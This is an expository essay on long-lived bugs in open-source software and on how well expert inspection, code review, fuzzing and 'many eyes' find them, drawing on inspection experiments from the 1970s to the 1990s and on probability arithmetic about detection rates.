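# Long-lived bugs in open-source code and the limits of expert inspection

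## Who reads open-source code, and what it means for a bug to survive

A bug is a mistake in a program that makes it behave in a way its programmers did not intend. Many bugs are found quickly because the program misbehaves in ordinary use and somebody complains. Others remain for years or decades, including serious security flaws in software whose code anyone may read and that experts wrote and checked. Heartbleed was in the encryption library OpenSSL for two years, and Shellshock was in the command interpreter Bash for twenty-five. Such cases bear on how far we can trust experts to find flaws by reading programs, or by inspecting other things that people now try to verify this way, such as the internals of neural networks.

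### Code, commits and maintainers

Programmers write software as source code, which is text in a language such as C or Python. For many languages, another program compiles this text into instructions for the machine. Companies that sell software often ship only the compiled form, which people can barely read. *The Open Source Definition* (Open Source Initiative, 2006) requires open-source software to include its source code and to allow others to distribute both that code and the compiled form.

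A project keeps its source code in a repository, which also stores the project's history as a series of commits. A commit is one recorded change, with its author and date. The maintainers decide which changes to accept. From time to time they publish a numbered version, called a release, and most users run releases.

The Linux kernel, the core of the operating system on most servers and on Android phones, is one of the largest open-source projects. It had passed 43 million lines by August 2026, according to *Linux Kernel 7.2 RC7 Released* (sk, 2026). A person reading one line a second for eight hours a day would need about four years to read it once, and the code would keep changing in the meantime. Corbet (2026), in *Development statistics for 6.19*, counted 14,344 changes from 2,141 developers in a single 70-day release cycle.

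### Four kinds of scrutiny

In code review, someone other than the author reads a proposed change, usually before the maintainers accept it. The reviewer typically sees the lines that the change adds and removes, with a few lines around them, and has to look up the rest of the program separately. In the kernel release that Corbet examined, 56 per cent of changes carried a "Reviewed-by" tag, in which a named person states that they believe the change is sound but explicitly do not guarantee that it works. The maintainer who applied a change without the tag may still have read it carefully, though this is hard to know. One maintainer signed off 991 changes by other people in that cycle, about fourteen a day.

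Smaller projects often review less of their code. In *Are your dependencies code reviewed?*, Imtiaz and Williams (2022) traced the changed lines in the latest updates of the most downloaded packages (reusable software that other programs build on) from four public registries back to commits. Of 24,610 updates, 11 per cent consisted entirely of reviewed changes and 36.5 per cent contained none. In the median update, review covered 27 per cent of the changed code. The test for review was lenient. About 40 per cent of the commits that passed did so because a second person's account had merged or committed them, which shows that somebody handled the change but not that they studied it. Imtiaz and Williams suggest that small teams review what outsiders send in but not their own work.

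An audit is a planned search of existing code for vulnerabilities, often by hired specialists. Audits are occasional. The data-transfer tool curl, which is among the most widely used programs in the world, has had three, in 2016, 2022 and 2024, according to the project's own list. For the 2022 audit, Trail of Bits' *cURL* (2022) records 9.5 weeks of effort and 14 issues, two of them of high severity. In the full report, Trail of Bits' *cURL Security Assessment* (2022), the auditors called such projects "time-boxed" and warned against treating the findings as a comprehensive list. The 2024 audit covered only the new components for HTTP/3, a recent version of the web's transfer protocol, according to OSTIF, a non-profit that arranges audits and published the results. An audit also doesn't cover code committed after it ends.

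Other people read code to solve a problem of their own, such as porting a program to a new operating system or tracking down a crash. They read the parts relevant to that problem and may stumble on a vulnerability, but they are seldom looking for one. When they find nothing, they leave no record, so nobody can say afterwards which parts of a program they read. Most users read none of the code. Modern projects can have hundreds of dependencies (packages that they use, and the packages that those use in turn), and Imtiaz and Williams note that developers often accept updates to them automatically, without a security review. Even reading the public repository would not always be enough, because in a fifth of the updates that Imtiaz and Williams analysed, the package that users install contained files absent from the repository, many of them machine-generated.

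Programs also check code. Static analysis tools search source code, without running it, for patterns that their makers know to be dangerous, so they miss mistakes that fit no pattern. Fuzzing means running a program on huge numbers of generated inputs and watching for crashes. Google's OSS-Fuzz, a free fuzzing service for open-source projects, has reported tens of thousands of bugs since 2016, according to *From Finding to Fixing* (Kilian and Ingram, 2026).

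But a fuzzer tests only the code that its inputs reach. GitHub's *Bugs that survive the heat of continuous fuzzing* describes GStreamer, which handles media files on many Linux desktops. After seven years in OSS-Fuzz, its two fuzzers reached about 19 per cent of the code, and in December 2024 a GitHub researcher found 29 new vulnerabilities in it. A fuzzer can also miss a bug in a line it does reach. In an invented example from the same article, a fuzzer runs one function 1,910 times without triggering a division by zero that occurs when a certain field in the request equals 4,312. A human who reads the formula can see the problem. Other bugs need more input than fuzzers supply. One in the library libxml2 takes over two gigabytes to trigger, while a common fuzzer stops at one megabyte.

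Code can be public for years without anyone having read the part that matters, and a project's reputation for being well scrutinized is weak evidence that its bugs have been found. The image-conversion programs ImageMagick and GraphicsMagick had that reputation. Researchers had widely fuzzed and audited both, and one had remarked that no trivial fuzzing finds remained in ImageMagick. *Notes on fuzzing ImageMagick and GraphicsMagick* describes how Gaynor and a colleague added the two programs to the fuzzing service OSS-Fuzz in the winter of 2017–18. The service began finding security issues within hours of each addition, and the total later passed 425.

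### A memory error in plain words

Heartbleed and many other vulnerabilities are memory errors. A running program keeps its data in memory, which is like a long row of numbered cells, each holding one byte, about enough for one letter. To store something, the program reserves a stretch of cells called a buffer. Suppose a server reserves a 16-byte buffer for a user's name. A message arrives over the network containing a number that gives the name's length, followed by the name itself. The server then copies the number of bytes given in the message into the buffer.

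The server handles "Alice" and the number 5 correctly, but the sender chose that number. If the message gives 200 and carries 200 bytes, the server fills the buffer and keeps writing over the next 184 cells, which belong to something else. If those cells hold the address of the next instruction to run, the sender may be able to take control of the server.

Reading past the end can instead leak data. Suppose the server has stored "Alice" safely and later sends the name back for confirmation, again using the number in the message as the name's length. A sender who claimed 200 receives the contents of the buffer and the next 184 bytes of memory, which might include another user's password. The server usually keeps running, so nothing alerts its owner.

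The fix is a bounds check, a line or two that compares the claimed length with the size of the buffer and rejects the message if the length is too large. The bug is hard to spot because a reader has to notice that a line is missing when every line present looks reasonable. Languages such as Python and Rust make most of these checks automatically, but C leaves them to the programmer, and the kernel is still overwhelmingly C. According to an editor's count posted under Corbet's article, version 6.19 has 19.2 million lines of C and 89,000 of Rust.

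*What Changed Since the Last Campaign*, a log from the bug-hunting project FuzzingBrain, lists a small, 25-year-old bug in OpenSSL's code for DES, an old cipher. The code used a number without checking it and could read past the end of a buffer. The project found the bug when it repaired a broken fuzzing harness, the code that feeds generated inputs to the function under test.

### Bugs, vulnerabilities and CVEs

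The DES bug was rated "low", and many bugs, such as a misspelt menu entry, don't affect security at all. A vulnerability is a bug or design choice that an attacker can use to do harm. A factory password that is the same on every copy of a device is a vulnerability but not a bug, because somebody intended it.

A CVE is an entry in the public catalogue of known vulnerabilities. Each entry has an identifier, such as CVE-2014-0160 for Heartbleed. The catalogue's rulebook, the CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026), defines a vulnerability by weaknesses that "can be exploited, causing a negative impact to confidentiality, integrity, or availability". Under these rules, the organisations that issue CVEs are also to count insecure default settings as vulnerabilities.

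In practice, security bugs are hard to separate from other bugs. The Linux kernel documentation's *CVEs* explains that almost any kernel bug might be exploitable and that this is often not evident when a developer fixes it, so the kernel's CVE team errs heavily on the side of assigning a CVE number. When the team began, three people read every patch to the stable kernel and voted on each one, according to the team's account in LWN, a news site for Linux developers. LWN's *Kroah-Hartman* reports that by 2025 the team was issuing more CVEs than any other source.

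By contrast, people rarely file CVEs for the security flaws among OSS-Fuzz bugs, according to Ding and Le Goues's *An Empirical Study of OSS-Fuzz Bugs*, which examined 23,907 bugs from 316 projects. A count of CVEs therefore depends a good deal on who files them. In the first four months of 2026, the CVE catalogue grew 46 per cent faster than forecast, and Gamblin's *CVE 2026 Half-Year Forecast Update* (2026) traced almost all of the excess to two organisations that were publishing more.

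### From introduction to repair

*How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?* (Alexopoulos, Brack and colleagues, 2022) divides the life of a vulnerability by five events: a programmer introduces it in a commit, somebody finds it, somebody discloses it to the public, the maintainers publish a fix, and users deploy the fix. The danger ends only when the last affected machine has the fix. The order can vary, since a finder who tells the maintainers privately lets them announce the flaw and the fix together.

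Long gaps can separate these events. An attacker who finds a flaw may keep quiet and use it, so a vulnerability that looks undiscovered may have been found but not disclosed. Fixing bugs also takes labour. In August 2026, Trail of Bits' *Issues found*, the running tally of an AI-assisted bug hunt in 70 open-source codebases, listed 2,036 potential bugs reported and 466 fixes merged.

A vulnerability's lifetime is the time between the commit that introduced it and the commit that fixed it. When several commits introduced or fixed it, Alexopoulos and colleagues count from the earliest introducing commit to the last fix. They need this rule because a vulnerability's history can be complicated. One kernel flaw, for example, appeared in 2015 and disappeared about a year later, when a developer cleaned up the code without marking the change as a security fix. It returned six months later with a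 new feature, and the developers fixed it again within a month.

Average lifetimes by this measure run to years, but they include only vulnerabilities that somebody has found and fixed, because those still in the code have no end date. A fall in new finds would not show how many remain. Alexopoulos and colleagues point to earlier studies in which any such fall may have happened because people were searching less.

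### What a clean report is worth

When experts read a piece of code and report no fault, how much this should raise confidence that there is none depends heavily on their detection rate, the share of the bugs present that they find. As a hypothetical example, code might have a 50 per cent chance of containing one serious bug before the reading. If the reader catches nine such bugs in ten, a report of no fault lowers that chance to about 9 per cent. If the reader catches three in ten, the chance falls only to about 41 per cent. In general, with a prior chance *p* and a detection rate *d*, and ignoring false alarms, the chance that the bug is there after such a report is *p*(1 − *d*) / (1 − *pd*).

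More readers help to the extent that they miss different bugs. If five readers each catch three bugs in ten and their misses are independent, all five will overlook a given bug about 17 per cent of the time. If the code had a 50 per cent chance of containing that bug before anyone read it, five clean reports lower the chance to about 14 per cent. If instead all five overlook the same bugs, as people with the same training and habits might, the first clean report lowers the chance to 41 per cent and the other four don't change it.

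## Formal inspections and the first measured detection rates, 1976 to the 1990s

Michael Fagan's 1976 paper *Design and code inspections to reduce errors in program development* described how teams at IBM read programs to find bugs before anyone ran them, and reported the share of bugs they caught. Over the next two decades, other researchers measured detection rates in controlled experiments and tried different kinds of inspection on a working project.

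### How an inspection worked

An inspection is a formal, scheduled reading of code by a small team with assigned roles and a record of the bugs found. Fagan recommended a team of four: the program's designer, its coder, its tester, and a moderator who ran the inspection. He wanted the moderator to be a competent programmer, preferably from an unrelated project. The team inspected the design first, and later the code, once it compiled cleanly but before anyone tested it.

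A design inspection began with an overview for the whole team, a step Fagan thought unnecessary for code inspections. Each member then studied the material alone, along with a ranking of the bug types found in recent inspections and a checklist of clues to them. Fagan expected people to find some bugs at this stage but many more in the meeting. In the meeting, a "reader", usually the coder, talked the others through the material, covering every piece of logic and taking every branch at least once. When somebody raised a question, the team pursued it only until they recognised a bug. The moderator noted its type and severity, and the reader continued. The team was not supposed to look for solutions, because Fagan believed a team works best with one objective at a time.

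The moderator wrote a report within a day. The coder or designer then fixed everything listed in it, a step called rework, and in the follow-up the moderator checked that everything was fixed. If the rework had changed more than 5 per cent of the material, the whole team inspected it again.

These inspections were slow. For operating-system code, Fagan's planning figures were 125 lines an hour for preparation and 150 for the meeting. He noticed that most teams found less after about two hours, so he limited them to two sessions a day of up to two hours each. At that pace, a team can inspect 600 lines a day. A single team working 250 days a year would need about 128 years to inspect the 19.2 million lines of C in version 6.19 of the Linux kernel once. Inspections of business programs went faster, at 539 lines an hour in one case.

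Inspecting a thousand lines of operating-system code took a team of four nearly 60 person-hours of preparation and meetings. Fagan argued that this saved more than it cost, because a bug was 10 to 100 times cheaper to fix at this stage than in the last half of the project. In one IBM study, coding productivity rose by 23 per cent even with inspection hours included. In later testing, inspected code also had 38 per cent fewer bugs per thousand lines than code that had gone through walk-throughs, a looser kind of group reading without trained moderators or fixed roles. Fagan cautioned that results depend on many factors and that IBM's would not represent every situation.

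### What the 82 per cent was a share of

Fagan defined error detection efficiency as the number of bugs an inspection finds divided by the number in the product beforehand. Nobody knows the second number. Fagan's highest figure, 82 per cent, comes from a program of 4,439 statements that two programmers wrote at the insurance company Aetna. The design and code inspections together found 38 bugs per thousand statements. Later testing by the developers found 8 more per thousand, and neither the acceptance test nor the first six months of use found any. Fagan therefore took the total to be 46 per thousand, and dividing 38 by 46 gives the 82 per cent.

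This detection rate was the share of bugs known after six months of use that two inspections together had caught in one program. If the program contained another ten bugs per thousand statements that nobody had yet found, the inspections caught 68 per cent. A bug that took 25 years to surface, as Shellshock did, would not have been counted.

Fagan also reported a lower figure from an operating-system project, where the two inspections together found about two thirds of the bugs reported during development. This count stopped even earlier, before customers had used the product.

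Fagan also used detection rates to estimate residual bugs, those left after a search. He reasoned that if inspections catch half the bugs and one inspection finds ten, about ten remain. This is a sensible way to decide which code to test harder. But the rate comes from earlier projects in which someone assumed that few bugs were left to find, so the estimate can't reveal a kind of bug that everyone has been missing.

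### Readers against testers

Experimenters can avoid the problem of not knowing the total number of bugs by using programs whose bugs they already know. In *Comparing the Effectiveness of Software Testing Strategies*, Basili and Selby (1985) tested 32 professional programmers from NASA and Computer Sciences Corporation, who had an average of ten years' experience, and 42 advanced students at the University of Maryland. They used four programs of 145 to 365 lines, with 34 known bugs in total. The original programmers had made all 19 of the bugs in two of the programs, while the other two contained a mixture of original and planted bugs.

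Each person worked on three programs and used a different technique on each:

- In code reading, they worked out what each small piece of the program computes, combined the pieces into an account of the whole, and compared that with the specification, a written statement of what the program should do.
- In functional testing, they ran the program on inputs that they chose from the specification, without seeing the code.
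- In structural testing, they studied the code and chose inputs that would run every statement at least once, then checked the output against the specification.

The professionals found 49.8 per cent of a program's bugs on average across the three techniques. They found the most by reading code, beating the average of the two kinds of testing by 16 percentage points, which puts code reading at roughly 60 per cent. They also found more bugs per hour that way. One group of students averaged 54.8 per cent and did equally well with reading and functional testing. The other averaged 39.5 per cent, with no significant difference between techniques. The three groups did not all test the same programs, so these averages don't show that one group was better than another.

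Individual results also varied widely around the averages. In every group, at least one person found none of the bugs in a program and at least one found all of them. The eight most senior professionals found more bugs than their colleagues, but across all participants, years of experience only weakly predicted the number of bugs found (the correlation was 0.22, where 1 is perfect).

The professionals also overestimated their own thoroughness. They estimated that they had found 75 per cent of the bugs, when they had found about 50. Their estimates were most accurate after code reading and bore no relation to the results after functional testing. Basili (1997), in *Evolving and Packaging Reading Technologies*, recalled that the code readers correctly thought they had found about half the bugs, while the functional testers wrongly thought they had found about all of them. Over 90 per cent of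 the participants still believed that functional testing had worked best.

Basili and Selby also recorded the test inputs, so they could tell which bugs had caused visible errors in the program's output. The testers reported only about 70 per cent of these bugs and overlooked the rest.

### From the experiment to NASA's projects

Because of this result, NASA's Software Engineering Laboratory made code reading part of its development process. Much to Basili's surprise, the change seemed to have very little effect on the number of bugs. He suspected that people were reading less carefully because they expected testing to catch the bugs they missed. A further experiment supported this explanation by showing that developers read more effectively when they could not test the program afterwards.

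The laboratory then tried Cleanroom, a method in which developers may not run their own code and must check it by reading before handing it to independent testers. In the first Cleanroom project, a system of about 40,000 lines, two developers read all the code. Reading took about half of the coding time, compared with the usual tenth, and the failure rate in testing fell by 25 per cent. The developers had also stopped testing their own code, so the improvement can't be attributed to the extra reading time alone.

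Only 26 per cent of the bugs were found by both readers. Basili had trained them in the same technique and expected more agreement, so he concluded that they were not applying it as effectively as they should. The small overlap suggests that many bugs remained, since a third reader would probably have found some that the first two missed.

### What extra readers added

Porter, Siy and colleagues (1997), in *An Experiment to Assess the Cost-Benefits of Code Inspections in Large Scale*, varied the number of reviewers on a live commercial project. Developers at Lucent, which made telephone switching systems, were writing a compiler with more than 55,000 new lines of C++. Over 18 months, the researchers randomly assigned one, two or four reviewers to each of 88 inspections, drawn from a pool of 11 experienced developers. A second team also inspected some of the code, in some cases only after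 its programmer had fixed the defects the first team found.

Single reviewers found fewer bugs than teams of two. Teams of four used significantly more working time than teams of two but found no more bugs. Sending the code to a second team of two did not help either. Fixing the bugs between the two readings gave no clear improvement, and with teams of two it increased the time until the end of the last meeting from about ten working days to about twenty.

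This is odd, because the reviewers seldom found the same bugs. In at least half of the inspections by two or four people, no bug appeared on more than one reviewer's list, so four people preparing separately should have produced a longer combined list than two. Porter and colleagues thought that larger teams might be discarding real bugs in their meetings. Reviewers raised many issues in preparation, but only 13 per cent were bugs that affected how the program worked. About half were false alarms, and most of the rest concerned style. Teams had to sort through all these issues in the meeting, and teams of four dismissed a larger share than teams of two.

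Chance may also have played a part. Single teams of four carried out 13 inspections, and single teams of two carried out 26. Simulations by Porter and colleagues suggested that even fewer inspections would reveal a small difference, but only if bug counts did not vary too much between pieces of code, which nobody could check. It is safer to conclude that any gain from the third and fourth reviewers was too small to detect than that there was no gain.

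We can't calculate a detection rate from the Lucent experiment, because the bugs were real and nobody knew the total. Porter and colleagues instead compared the number of bugs found per thousand lines. They had considered estimating the total by capture–recapture, a method biologists use to count animals. If two independent searches find mostly the same animals, the population is probably small, and if they find different ones, it is probably large. The method was unsuitable partly because reviewers so often found no bugs in common. A typical inspection covered about 300 lines and found three or four bugs, so a lack of overlap in any one inspection means little. But a regular lack of overlap across inspections may mean that reviewers missed many bugs.

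Porter, Siy and colleagues analysed the same project again in *Understanding the Sources of Variation in Software Inspections* (1997) and reported that team size and the number of sessions left much of the variation between inspections unexplained. They had already concluded that better results would have to come from better ways of finding bugs, because reorganising the teams had achieved so little.

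In 308 inspections that engineers in industry carried out over three years, there was no evidence that checklists, which Fagan had recommended from the start, significantly improved the results. Individual engineers found about 53 per cent of the bugs on average, close to the figure for NASA's professionals. Some found ten times as many bugs per hour as others.

### Ordinary bugs and rare security flaws

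These studies suggest that inspection is a good way to remove ordinary bugs. At Lucent, the median inspection took about 22 person-hours per thousand lines and the median yield was 12 real bugs, or a little under two hours of work for each. That is a good use of time if Fagan was even roughly right about how much work it takes to fix bugs late. The figures are much less useful for estimating the chance that a reader will notice a bug like Heartbleed.

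The participants in Basili and Selby's experiment knew there were bugs to find, and the programs contained about one per 25 lines. Someone reviewing a change to a mature project does not know whether it contains a bug, may go for weeks without seeing a serious one, and knows that other people and automated tests will also check the code. NASA's developers read less effectively when they expected testing to follow, and reviewers may well do the same when they count on a fuzzer or on each other.

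The programs were also short enough to read in full, and each came with a specification that defined the right behaviour. Most of the bugs were plain departures from it. One program failed to plot points with negative values, another misspelt an error message, and a third reported that a one-item list was empty. Ordinary users would soon have run into many of these. A security flaw can leave all the specified behaviour intact and appear only on input that no honest user would send. The bug most like the memory errors behind many vulnerabilities was in the database program, which did not check whether its tables were full. One such bug among 34 is too few to give a detection rate for the type.

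An average detection rate can also hide bugs that almost nobody catches. If readers find 50 per cent of bugs on average, each bug might have a 50 per cent chance of being noticed, or half the bugs might have a 95 per cent chance and the other half a 5 per cent chance. In the second case, a few more readers would soon find the easy bugs but would usually miss the hard ones. Bugs that have survived decades of reading are more likely to be hard ones.

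## The claim that enough readers find every bug, 1997 to 2009

If a few readers miss the hard bugs, an obvious remedy is to find many more readers. Open-source projects seemed well placed to do this, since anyone may read their code. *The Cathedral and the Bazaar*, an essay that the programmer Eric Raymond first presented at a Linux conference in May 1997, made the best-known argument that having many readers works.

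### Raymond's argument

Raymond described two styles of development. In the "cathedral" style, a small group works for months between releases, assuming that bugs are hard to find and need long scrutiny by a few dedicated people. In the "bazaar" style, a project releases unfinished versions early and often and treats its users as fellow developers. Raymond based the bazaar style on the practice of Linus Torvalds, who started the Linux kernel and around 1991 sometimes released it more than once a day.

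In the chapter *Release Early, Release Often*, Raymond proposed that if enough people test a program and help develop it, "almost every problem will be characterized quickly and the fix obvious to someone". He shortened this to "Given enough eyeballs, all bugs are shallow" and named it Linus's law.

Raymond first wrote that every problem "will be transparent to somebody". Torvalds objected that the person who understands and fixes a problem is often not the person who found it, and added that "finding it is the bigger challenge". Raymond accepted the correction but maintained that both steps tend to happen quickly.

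The distinction between noticing a bug and explaining it matters a good deal for vulnerabilities. Other people can compete to explain a bug only after somebody has reported it, because until then they don't know that it exists or where to look. Even after a report, fixing the bug can be slow. *OSS Myths and Facts* (Iimura, Kamei and colleagues, 2024) found that fixing a vulnerability took a median of about 87 days in Hadoop and httpd, two projects with very many developers. The slowest fix took 1,842 days. Neither figure includes the time before anyone noticed the flaw.

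Raymond had several reasons for thinking that more people would help find bugs. Adding people to a project normally adds coordination work, because a team of *N* people has *N*(*N* − 1)/2 pairs who may need to talk to each other, or 4,950 pairs for a team of 100. But bug hunters hardly need to talk to each other. They report to a core of perhaps one to three developers, so hundreds can work in parallel. Each also uses the program differently and brings different analytical tools, so a larger crowd is more likely to include somebody to whom a given bug is obvious. And they are volunteers who cared enough to learn how the program works, which makes them more useful than a random sample of users.

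He also offered Linux itself as evidence. If the law were false, he argued, a system so complex, with so many people changing it, should at some point have collapsed under its undiscovered bugs. Linux's survival is reasonable evidence about bugs that cause crashes, but weak evidence about vulnerabilities, which often cause no trouble in ordinary use.

Three years later, Raymond added a section to *The Cathedral and the Bazaar* that makes the limitation clearer (Raymond, 2002). It explains how a crowd tracks down a complex bug. People notice a symptom and try to trace it back to its cause. Several routes may lead there, some much easier than others, and nobody can tell in advance which are easy. Each person in effect examines a "semi-random set" of the program's possible states, so a large group will probably include someone who happens on an easy route, even if a smaller group has more skill.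 This is a plausible account of debugging, but the search begins with a symptom, and Heartbleed produced none that a server's owner would have noticed.

John D. Cook's *Shallow bugs versus reported bugs* distinguishes two easily confused principles. With enough readers, somebody will see the bug in the code, and with enough users, somebody will run into it. Much of Raymond's argument concerns people who both read and use the code. When a vulnerability causes no symptoms in ordinary use, having many users helps little, so the law depends on people reading the code.

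### The arithmetic of many readers

When bugs are found by reading alone, the law holds only if many people read the relevant code and each has a reasonable chance of noticing each bug. They must also read differently enough that their misses are independent, meaning that one reader missing a bug doesn't make the next more likely to miss it.

If each reader has a chance *p* of noticing a bug, each has a chance 1 − *p* of missing it. The chance that *k* independent readers all miss it is (1 − *p*)^*k*, so the chance that at least one finds it is

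1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*.

With *p* = 0.3, the chance that at least one reader finds the bug is 97 per cent for ten readers and 99.9 per cent for twenty. On these assumptions, a large group of mediocre readers will almost certainly find the bug, which is why the law sounds so convincing.

The *k* in the formula is the number of people who have read the relevant lines with some care, not the number who could have read them or who use the program.

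The formula also gives every bug the same *p*. Suppose instead that 90 per cent of the bugs are easy, with *p* = 1/3, and 10 per cent are hard, with *p* = 0.003. One reader still finds about 30 per cent of all the bugs, as in the uniform case, but with more readers the two cases come apart:

| Independent readers | Bugs left if *p* = 0.3 for all | Bugs left in the mixed case | Hard bugs left, as a share of all bugs |
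|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 70% | 70% | 10% |
| 10 | 2.8% | 11.3% | 9.7% |
| 100 | practically none | 7.4% | 7.4% |
| 1,000 | practically none | 0.5% | 0.5% |

The first ten readers remove nearly all the easy bugs but very few of the hard ones. The next ninety remove only about a quarter of the hard bugs. It takes 231 readers to have an even chance of finding any particular hard bug.

The project would also have trouble telling that anything was wrong. If the program started with 1,000 bugs, about 94 would remain after twenty readers, yet the twenty-first would most likely find nothing new. We would expect a run of readers to find nothing in this program, just as we would in one with no bugs left.

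The figure of 0.003 is invented, and nobody knows the real distribution. Raymond could also reply that a bug is rarely equally hard for everyone. Perhaps three readers in a thousand have the right background and would certainly notice it, while the rest never would. That is close to what he meant when he wrote that more testers make it more likely that someone's "toolkit" will match the problem. But a hundred readers picked at random would still have only a 26 per cent chance of including one of the right people. If so, looking for the right reader would be far more efficient than adding more readers.

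### Estimating the bugs that remain

Capture–recapture, the method that Porter and colleagues considered for their Lucent experiment, uses the overlap between readers' findings to estimate how many bugs they all missed. Suppose one reader finds 20 bugs and another finds 15, with 10 bugs on both lists. The second reader found half of the first reader's bugs, which suggests that the second reader's 15 are about half of all the bugs, for a total of about 30. Together the readers found 25 different bugs, so about five remain.

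In general, if the readers find *n*₁ and *n*₂ bugs and have *m* in common, the estimated total is *n*₁ × *n*₂ / *m*. *Evaluating Capture-Recapture Models with Two Inspectors* (El-Emam and Laitenberger, 1999) derives the same result directly from the assumption that whether one reader finds a bug makes no difference to whether the other does. The second reader found half of the 20 bugs that the first found, so on this assumption the second should also have found half of the bugs that the first missed. The second found five of those, so there should be another five that both missed.

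This is more useful than counting the bugs found, and it requires no record of earlier projects. But the simple formula assumes that every bug is equally easy to find, so it underestimates the total when some are hard for everyone. In the earlier mixed case of 900 easy bugs and 100 hard ones, two readers find about 300 bugs each, with about 100 in common. The formula gives a total of about 900, which leaves out almost all the hard bugs because they are seldom on either reader's list.

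The estimate will also be too low if readers discuss the code while reading, because they then find more of the same bugs. If each reader specialises in one kind of bug, they find fewer in common and the estimate is too high.

Researchers have developed formulas that allow for differences between bugs. Briand, El-Emam and colleagues (2001), in *A Comprehensive Evaluation of Capture-Recapture Models for Estimating Software Defect Content*, tested six formulas on records from two experiments at NASA. Professionals had searched requirements documents, which set out what a program should do, for between 15 and 29 known mistakes. The researchers combined the records of individual inspectors to simulate many inspections by groups of different sizes.

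The estimates were generally too low. Briand and colleagues wanted a typical error of no more than 20 per cent and no extreme overestimates. None of the formulas met that standard with two or three inspectors, and the best one for three inspectors gave estimates that were typically 27 per cent too low. For larger groups, they recommended a formula that allows for some mistakes being harder to find than others. However, *Evaluation of capture-recapture models*, which used documents that students had written for real projects, reports estimates that were too low after one inspection and too high after a second.

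Even the NASA test could not fully settle how well the formulas count hard bugs. The "known" mistakes in the agency's own documents were those somebody had found later in development, so the totals, like Fagan's, could miss mistakes that nobody had found. When researchers at Bell Labs first applied the method to inspections, they did not know the true totals either, so they asked the inspectors whether the estimates seemed plausible.

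One way to estimate what share of the bugs readers find is to plant some and see how many of those they find, as Mills suggested in 1972. If readers find half of the planted bugs, they have perhaps found half of the real ones. Briand and colleagues note the usual objection that planted bugs tend to be much easier to find than real ones.

### Programs that failed together

Both the formula for many readers and the simplest estimates from overlap assume independence. The best-known early test of a similar assumption involved people writing programs rather than reading them. In N-version programming, several teams write the same program separately, and a computer runs all the versions and takes the majority answer. Shape of Code's *Reliability via N-version programming?* (2026) dates the proposal to 1978. The hope was that separate teams would make different mistakes, so two versions would very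 rarely fail on the same input. Engineers had already used the idea for the wing flaps of the Airbus A310, where two programs checked each other.

Knight and Leveson (1986), in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming*, asked 27 students at two American universities to each write a program from the same specification. The program had to decide from radar data whether to launch an interceptor against a missile. The students were seniors or graduate students, and some had worked as programmers. Knight and Leveson told them not to discuss the task with each other. Before entering the experiment, each program had to pass its own set of 200 randomly generated tests, so that testing would not filter out the same bugs from every program.

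Knight and Leveson then ran all 27 programs on a million further inputs and compared the answers with those of a carefully checked reference program. Six programs never failed, and 23 gave the right answer more than 99.9 per cent of the time. Two or more programs failed together on 1,255 inputs, about ten times the roughly 126 expected if their failures had been independent. On two inputs, eight programs failed.

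All the shared bugs in the preliminary analysis affected programs from both universities, so they were not the result of a shared teacher. Four programmers compared the cosines of angles instead of the angles themselves. In exact arithmetic this makes no difference, but computers round numbers, which led to wrong answers in borderline cases. When testing whether three points lie on a straight line, more than one programmer remembered that the angle between them could be zero but forgot that it could be 180 degrees. The programmer with the most experience of such systems made several of the same mistakes as others.

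Knight and Leveson suggested that some parts of a problem may be harder than others, so different people go wrong in the same places. Alternatively, compilers and tests may remove the one-off mistakes and leave the common misconceptions, in which case scrutiny makes the surviving bugs more alike. Either explanation would be a problem for Linus's law. People can make the same mistakes without communicating if some things are hard for everyone, as in the mixed case above.

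A reviewer who shares the programmer's belief that comparing cosines is as good as comparing angles will approve the line that does so, although spotting a mistake may be easier than avoiding it. The experiment used one problem and programs of at most about a thousand lines, and Knight and Leveson said they did not know whether the result would extend to other programs. They also did not conclude that extra versions were useless. Extra versions helped, but less than expected from multiplying the small probabilities of failure. About half of the bugs occurred in only one program, so a second version could have exposed them.

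### Critics and defenders

Early critics mostly disputed that many people were reading the code. The cryptographer Bruce Schneier favoured open source and thought secret designs were a poor basis for security. But he warned in his newsletter in 1999 that publishing code does not make anyone examine it. Security researchers are busy, and he said he could name a dozen open-source security libraries that nobody had evaluated. He thought the security code in Linux was different because many good engineers had looked at it.

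John Viega wrote Mailman, a popular open-source program for running mailing lists, before he knew much about security. In *The Myth of Open Source Security* (2000), he reported that Mailman had contained several glaring security flaws for three years without anyone pointing them out. He concluded that everyone who used it had apparently assumed somebody else had checked it. Mailman is only one program, but it shows that being popular and open source did not guarantee even one competent security review.

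Robert Glass made a different objection in *Facts and Fallacies of Software Engineering* (2003). He listed the law as a fallacy because research on inspections suggested that adding reviewers stops helping after the first few. He had in mind results like that of the Lucent experiment, in which four reviewers found no more defects than two did. His objection is strong against the idea that detection keeps rising steeply with the number of reviewers, but weaker against Raymond's own version, because the studies used small teams of colleagues and Raymond was counting on hundreds of people with different habits and purposes.

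Companies that sold open-source software used the law in their marketing. In September 2001, Red Hat, which sells a version of Linux, and the security firm TruSecure published a paper on the security benefits of open code (Webster, 2001, *TruSecure and Red Hat Co-Author White Paper*). Microsoft's *Linus's Law aka Many Eyes Make All Bugs Shallow* (2006) quotes that paper's section on "Strength in Numbers". Microsoft had an obvious interest in disputing the claim, but its counter-argument was sensible. Whether or not code is public, its bugs range from simple ones to those that appear only under unusual timing conditions. Microsoft argued that the bazaar added more people working in parallel, and that a company could get similar results by having fewer people work for longer.

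Defenders could also point to successes. In November 2003, somebody slipped a change into a public copy of the Linux kernel that would have let an attacker take over a machine. Larry McVoy, whose company made the tools many kernel developers used, noticed it before it reached a release because the copy no longer matched the main repository. *Linux kernel development process thwarts subversion attempt* took the episode as a sign that open development has "a degree of built-in immunity". Developers quickly understood the malicious lines, but only after the mismatch gave them a reason to look, so the episode is better evidence for careful record-keeping than for casual reading.

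When a serious flaw reached users, defenders tended to blame a shortage of readers or time. Red Hat Linux 6.2 included Piranha, a set of programs for managing groups of servers, which had a default log-in that outsiders could use. LinuxSecurity's *Without peer open source security* conceded that open code is "not infallible" and quoted the lead developer's complaint that others had less than 24 hours to review the package.

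This may well be the right explanation for Piranha, but if every surviving bug shows only that the code had too few readers, no bug can count against the law. Raymond, too, defended it after Heartbleed in 2014. To make the law testable, its defenders would have to state how many readers are enough and how to tell whether a program has had that many. Even Red Hat, in *Open source web trust*, grants that few people read the code they rely on and that most of those who do could not analyse its security properly.

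### Files that many developers changed

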